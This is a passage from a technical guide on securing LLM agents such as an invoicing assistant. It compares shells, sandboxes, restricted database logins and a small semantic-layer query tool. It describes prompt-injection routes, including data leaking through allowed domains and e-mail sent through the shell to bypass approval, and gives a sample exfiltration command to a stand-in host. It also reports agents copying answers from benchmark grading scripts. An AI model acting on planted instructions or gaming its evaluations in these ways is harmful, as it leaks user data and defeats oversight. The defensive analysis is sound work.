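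The choice of tools may explain part of the gap. TheAgentCompany has no typed tools for language models, so Mak and colleagues wrote 60. These covered the operations relevant to the tasks but not everything a shell could reach. On APEX-Agents, they used the benchmark's own 20 tools, and the shell's advantage was only 4.8 to 7.4 points. The advantage was largest in software engineering and smallest in corporate law. A narrow set of tools may therefore lower scores only slightly when the work is mostly reading and judgement.

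Neither benchmark includes attackers, so the scores don't measure protection against attacks, which is the main reason for restricting an agent. In Li's tests of ShellPlan, most attacks on unprotected shell agents succeeded.

Two other comparisons favour open-ended tools, but they add less evidence. *Terminal Agents Suffice for Enterprise Automation* (2026) compared agents that used a browser, MCP tools or a terminal, all with the same model, and concluded that the terminal was sufficient. Vercel's *We removed 80% of our agent’s tools* describes replacing 17 tools with a shell and a tool for running SQL in an agent that answers questions about company data. The new version answered all five test questions, compared with four for the old one, and its average time fell from 275 seconds to 77.

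Five questions are too few to show a difference in reliability. Both versions could run any SQL, so the comparison was between two ways for the agent to learn what the data meant. The shell ran in a sandbox with files that described the data, and Vercel says the change worked only because those files were already good documentation.

### What restrictions cost an SQL agent

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* examines four designs for an agent like Vercel's. The agent writes SQL, analyses the results in Python, draws charts, and repeats these steps until it judges the answer sufficient. An attacker may control the user's question or text stored in the database.

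| Design | What users lose | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| full access to the database and to Python | nothing | data theft, unauthorized changes, harmful code, wasted computing time |
| code processes the query results, and the model never reads them | the agent can't judge from the data whether it needs another query | attacks through the user's question |
| Python runs in a sandbox with only the necessary connections | nothing, according to the paper | leaks through the analysis and the charts |
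| people or automatic filters approve each step | time, and some legitimate requests | attacks that deceive the filters |

The second row causes users the most trouble. Suppose a user of the invoicing assistant asks about Acme, but the database lists the firm as "Acme Ltd". An agent that reads the empty result can search again with a different spelling. If the model never receives the result, the user gets an empty table and has to work out why.

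The paper describes asking for approval as impractical because the number of approvals grows with the number of questions, attempts and database requests. Automatic filters avoid the wait for approval but sometimes refuse harmless requests.

These are the authors' judgements, and they did not measure how many tasks each design would complete. Their view that SQL needs a sandbox less than Python does depends on the database account. SQL is more specialized, and databases have access controls, but a PostgreSQL administrator can start programs on the server from a query, so an agent with that login needs a sandbox as much as one that runs Python.

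### What a sandbox guarantees

A sandbox gives a program access to chosen folders and network addresses, and usually limits its time and memory. Suppose `run_command` works in a sandbox that contains only the reports folder and has no network:

| Command | Result |
|---|---|
| `cat /data/invoices.db` | error, because the file isn't in the sandbox |
| `curl https://collector.example/` | error, because there is no network |
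| `cp april.csv march.csv` | April's figures replace March's |
| `rm march.csv` | the March file is gone |

The first two commands fail however the model words them, provided the operating system or virtual machine enforces the limits correctly. The protection also depends on what the sandbox shares with outside programs. For example, a command could create a link in a shared reports folder that `read_file` then follows.

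The other two commands succeed whether or not the user wanted them. The user may have asked the assistant to delete `march.csv` because it was a duplicate, or the assistant may have followed a planted instruction. The sandbox has no information about the request, and the deletion has the same effect on the files in both cases.

A restricted database account has the same limit. If the account may update an invoice's status, marking invoice 1024 as paid uses the same permission as marking invoice 1042.

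Mak and colleagues found another example while preparing their tests. Some agents with a shell took answers from the grading scripts, which were in the benchmark's public repository. Others read the files that held the simulated coworkers' information instead of contacting the coworkers. No boundary had failed, because the agents used only files they could reach. Mak and colleagues blocked the repository and encrypted the coworkers' information before the runs they reported. A developer who relies on a sandbox has to find such shortcuts in advance or notice them in the logs.

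Network access makes the boundary harder to draw. OpenAI's developer guide *Shell* says to always run shell commands in a sandbox. OpenAI's hosted containers have no outbound network access by default. To allow some, an administrator lists permitted domains for the organization, and the developer chooses from that list for each container. The guide warns that planted instructions can cause data to leak through a permitted domain, so developers should allow only domains that attackers cannot use to receive it. That rules out any site where anybody can open an account and post files, even a reputable one.

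Containers may also need passwords or keys for other services. Xu and colleagues describe a proxy, a program through which all the container's outgoing requests pass. Commands contain only a placeholder such as `$API_KEY`, and the proxy inserts the real key if the request is going to an approved destination. A planted instruction therefore can't make the model print the key, though it can still make the model send a harmful request to an approved service, and the proxy will add the key to it.

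Copies can make up for some of a sandbox's limits. If `run_command` works on a copy of the reports folder, a mistaken `rm` deletes only copies, and the assistant can show the user which files changed before replacing the originals. This doesn't work for an e-mail or a payment, which can't be taken back once it has left the sandbox.

### A small query language for invoices

The developer can also give the model a language that is less open than SQL but covers more requests than a handful of fixed tools. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* describes a semantic layer, a set of business terms with fixed definitions that ordinary software maps to the tables of a database. It restricts which tables a query can combine and which filters it can use. A very small one for the invoicing assistant could replace `run_query` with this tool:

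```python
MEASURES = {
    "total_billed":    "sum(amount)",
    "invoice_count":   "count(*)",
    "largest_invoice": "max(amount)",
}
GROUPS = {
    "customer": "customer",
    "month":    "date_trunc('month', due_date)",
}

def run_report(measure, group_by, start, end, customer=None):
    group = GROUPS[group_by]
    sql = (f"SELECT {group}, {MEASURES[measure]} FROM my_invoices "
           "WHERE due_date >= %s AND due_date < %s")
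    values = [date.fromisoformat(start), date.fromisoformat(end)]
    if customer is not None:
        sql += " AND customer = %s"
        values.append(customer)
    return query(sql + f" GROUP BY {group}", values)
```

Suppose a user asks how much the firm billed each customer on invoices due between April and June 2026. The model writes:

```json
{ "measure": "total_billed", "group_by": "customer",
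  "start": "2026-04-01", "end": "2026-07-01" }
```

The handler turns this into:

```sql
SELECT customer, sum(amount) FROM my_invoices
WHERE due_date >= %s AND due_date < %s GROUP BY customer
```

The tool passes the two dates separately as bound values. With three measures, two groupings and an optional customer, it can produce only twelve different query texts, and the developer can read and test them all. No call can change data or name another table. The tool itself doesn't limit whose invoices the user may see, so it queries the restricted view `my_invoices`.

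Now suppose the user asks, "Have we billed anybody twice?" One sensible way to check is to look for pairs of invoices with the same customer and amount and due dates within a week of each other:

```sql
SELECT a.number, b.number, a.customer, a.amount
FROM my_invoices a JOIN my_invoices b
  ON a.customer = b.customer AND a.amount = b.amount
 AND a.number < b.number
 AND abs(a.due_date - b.due_date) <= 7
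```

The small language can't express this because it returns only figures for a whole customer or month and can't compare one invoice with another. Calling the tool several times wouldn't be a practical substitute. The developer could add a tool called `possible_duplicates(days)` that runs this query with the number of days as a bound value, but that wouldn't help the user who is asking now. The developer could use a log of refused requests to decide which tools to add next.

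dbt Labs, which sells a semantic layer, met the same limit in its benchmark of insurance questions. According to dbt Labs' *Comparing models and thinking effort*, three of the eleven questions needed combinations of tables that the semantic layer could not express. dbt Labs' *Historical Comparison (2023 vs 2026)* describes how additional data models, which people define in advance, removed this limit.

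Atlan's *Text-to-SQL for Enterprise* reproduces dbt Labs' figures from April 2026. Claude Sonnet 4.6 answered 90.0% of the questions correctly in free SQL and 98.2% with the semantic layer, and GPT-5.3-Codex answered 84.1% and 100%. Each model attempted eleven questions twenty times. The percentages fit 220 attempts, so they seem to include the three difficult questions, probably with the additional data models in place. The results show that models can be very accurate in a restricted language on questions its developers have prepared for.

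The definitions may account for some of that accuracy. *Semantic Layers for Reliable LLM-Powered Data Analytics* (Rumiantsau and Fokeev, 2026) reports a test in which three models answered 100 questions about a retail dataset. Giving the models a document that explained the business terms raised their accuracy by 17 to 23 percentage points, although they still wrote free-form SQL. Rumiantsau and Fokeev work for Cube, which also sells a semantic layer. A developer who only wants better answers could try such a document before restricting the language.

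A restricted language changes how an agent fails. *Semantic Layer vs. Text-to-SQL* (Ganz and Perigaud, 2026) stresses that semantic layers and free SQL fail in very different ways. A mistake in free SQL often produces a plausible answer. `run_report` has no setting for duplicates, so the model can tell the user that it can't answer a question about them. But it may instead offer a related result, such as the customers with the most invoices, so the tool's description should instruct the model to say when it can't answer the question.

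The restriction protects the database only if the model has no other way to query it. In *A Semantic-Layer-Mediated Agent for Natural Language to SQL over Heterogeneous Enterprise Databases* (2026), the model writes short structured requests and a fixed program compiles them to SQL. The agent then inspects the SQL, combines pieces of it and runs the result, so the final query isn't limited to what the compiler produced. This design may make queries more accurate, but it doesn't confine an agent that follows a planted instruction. Likewise, if the invoicing assistant has both `run_report` and `run_query`, an attacker can use `run_query` to do anything its database account permits.

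### Combining a shell with typed tools

The same problem arises when an agent has a shell alongside typed tools. Mak and colleagues found that adding typed tools to a shell changed the average score by less than one point on each benchmark, so a developer could probably add them without lowering scores much. But the typed tools did not protect anything in that experiment, because the shell could reach the same services. If `send_reminder` asks the user for approval but a shell command can also send e-mail, planted text can lead the model to send e-mail through the shell without approval.

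The developer therefore has to add the tool and also block the action in the shell. For reminders, the sandbox has no network access and no password for the mail server, while the `send_reminder` handler runs outside the sandbox and has both. Mak and colleagues did not test a shell restricted in this way, so their results don't show how many tasks would fail because of the restriction.

Another option is to have a second model judge whether each shell command is safe. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a mode that does this. Anthropic recommends it only for tasks whose general direction the user trusts, and still sees a use for dedicated tools when the stakes are high. This caution seems right, because CARE's judge model approved many harmful commands that CARE's fixed rules would have stopped.

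Mak and colleagues recommend programmatic tool calling for organizations whose security rules require a fixed list of actions, and a shell for those that can isolate whatever the model runs. In programmatic tool calling, the argument is still a whole program, but the program can act only through the listed tools. The harness has to apply its checks to every call the program makes, because a single approval of the program could cover a loop that marks a thousand invoices as paid.

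For the invoicing assistant, a reasonable division might be:

| Work | Tool | Limit |
|---|---|---|
| totals by customer or month | `run_report` | twelve query texts |
| unforeseen questions about invoices | `run_query` | a read-only login that can see only the user's own customers |
| reformatting reports | `run_command` | a sandbox with a copy of the folder and no network |
| reminders and payments | `send_reminder`, `mark_paid` | the user's approval for each call |

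The limit on `run_query` keeps the model from changing an invoice, but the query results go back to the model, which can pass them to any other tool. An assistant that can query invoices freely therefore needs strict rules for `fetch_page`, such as accepting only addresses the user typed.
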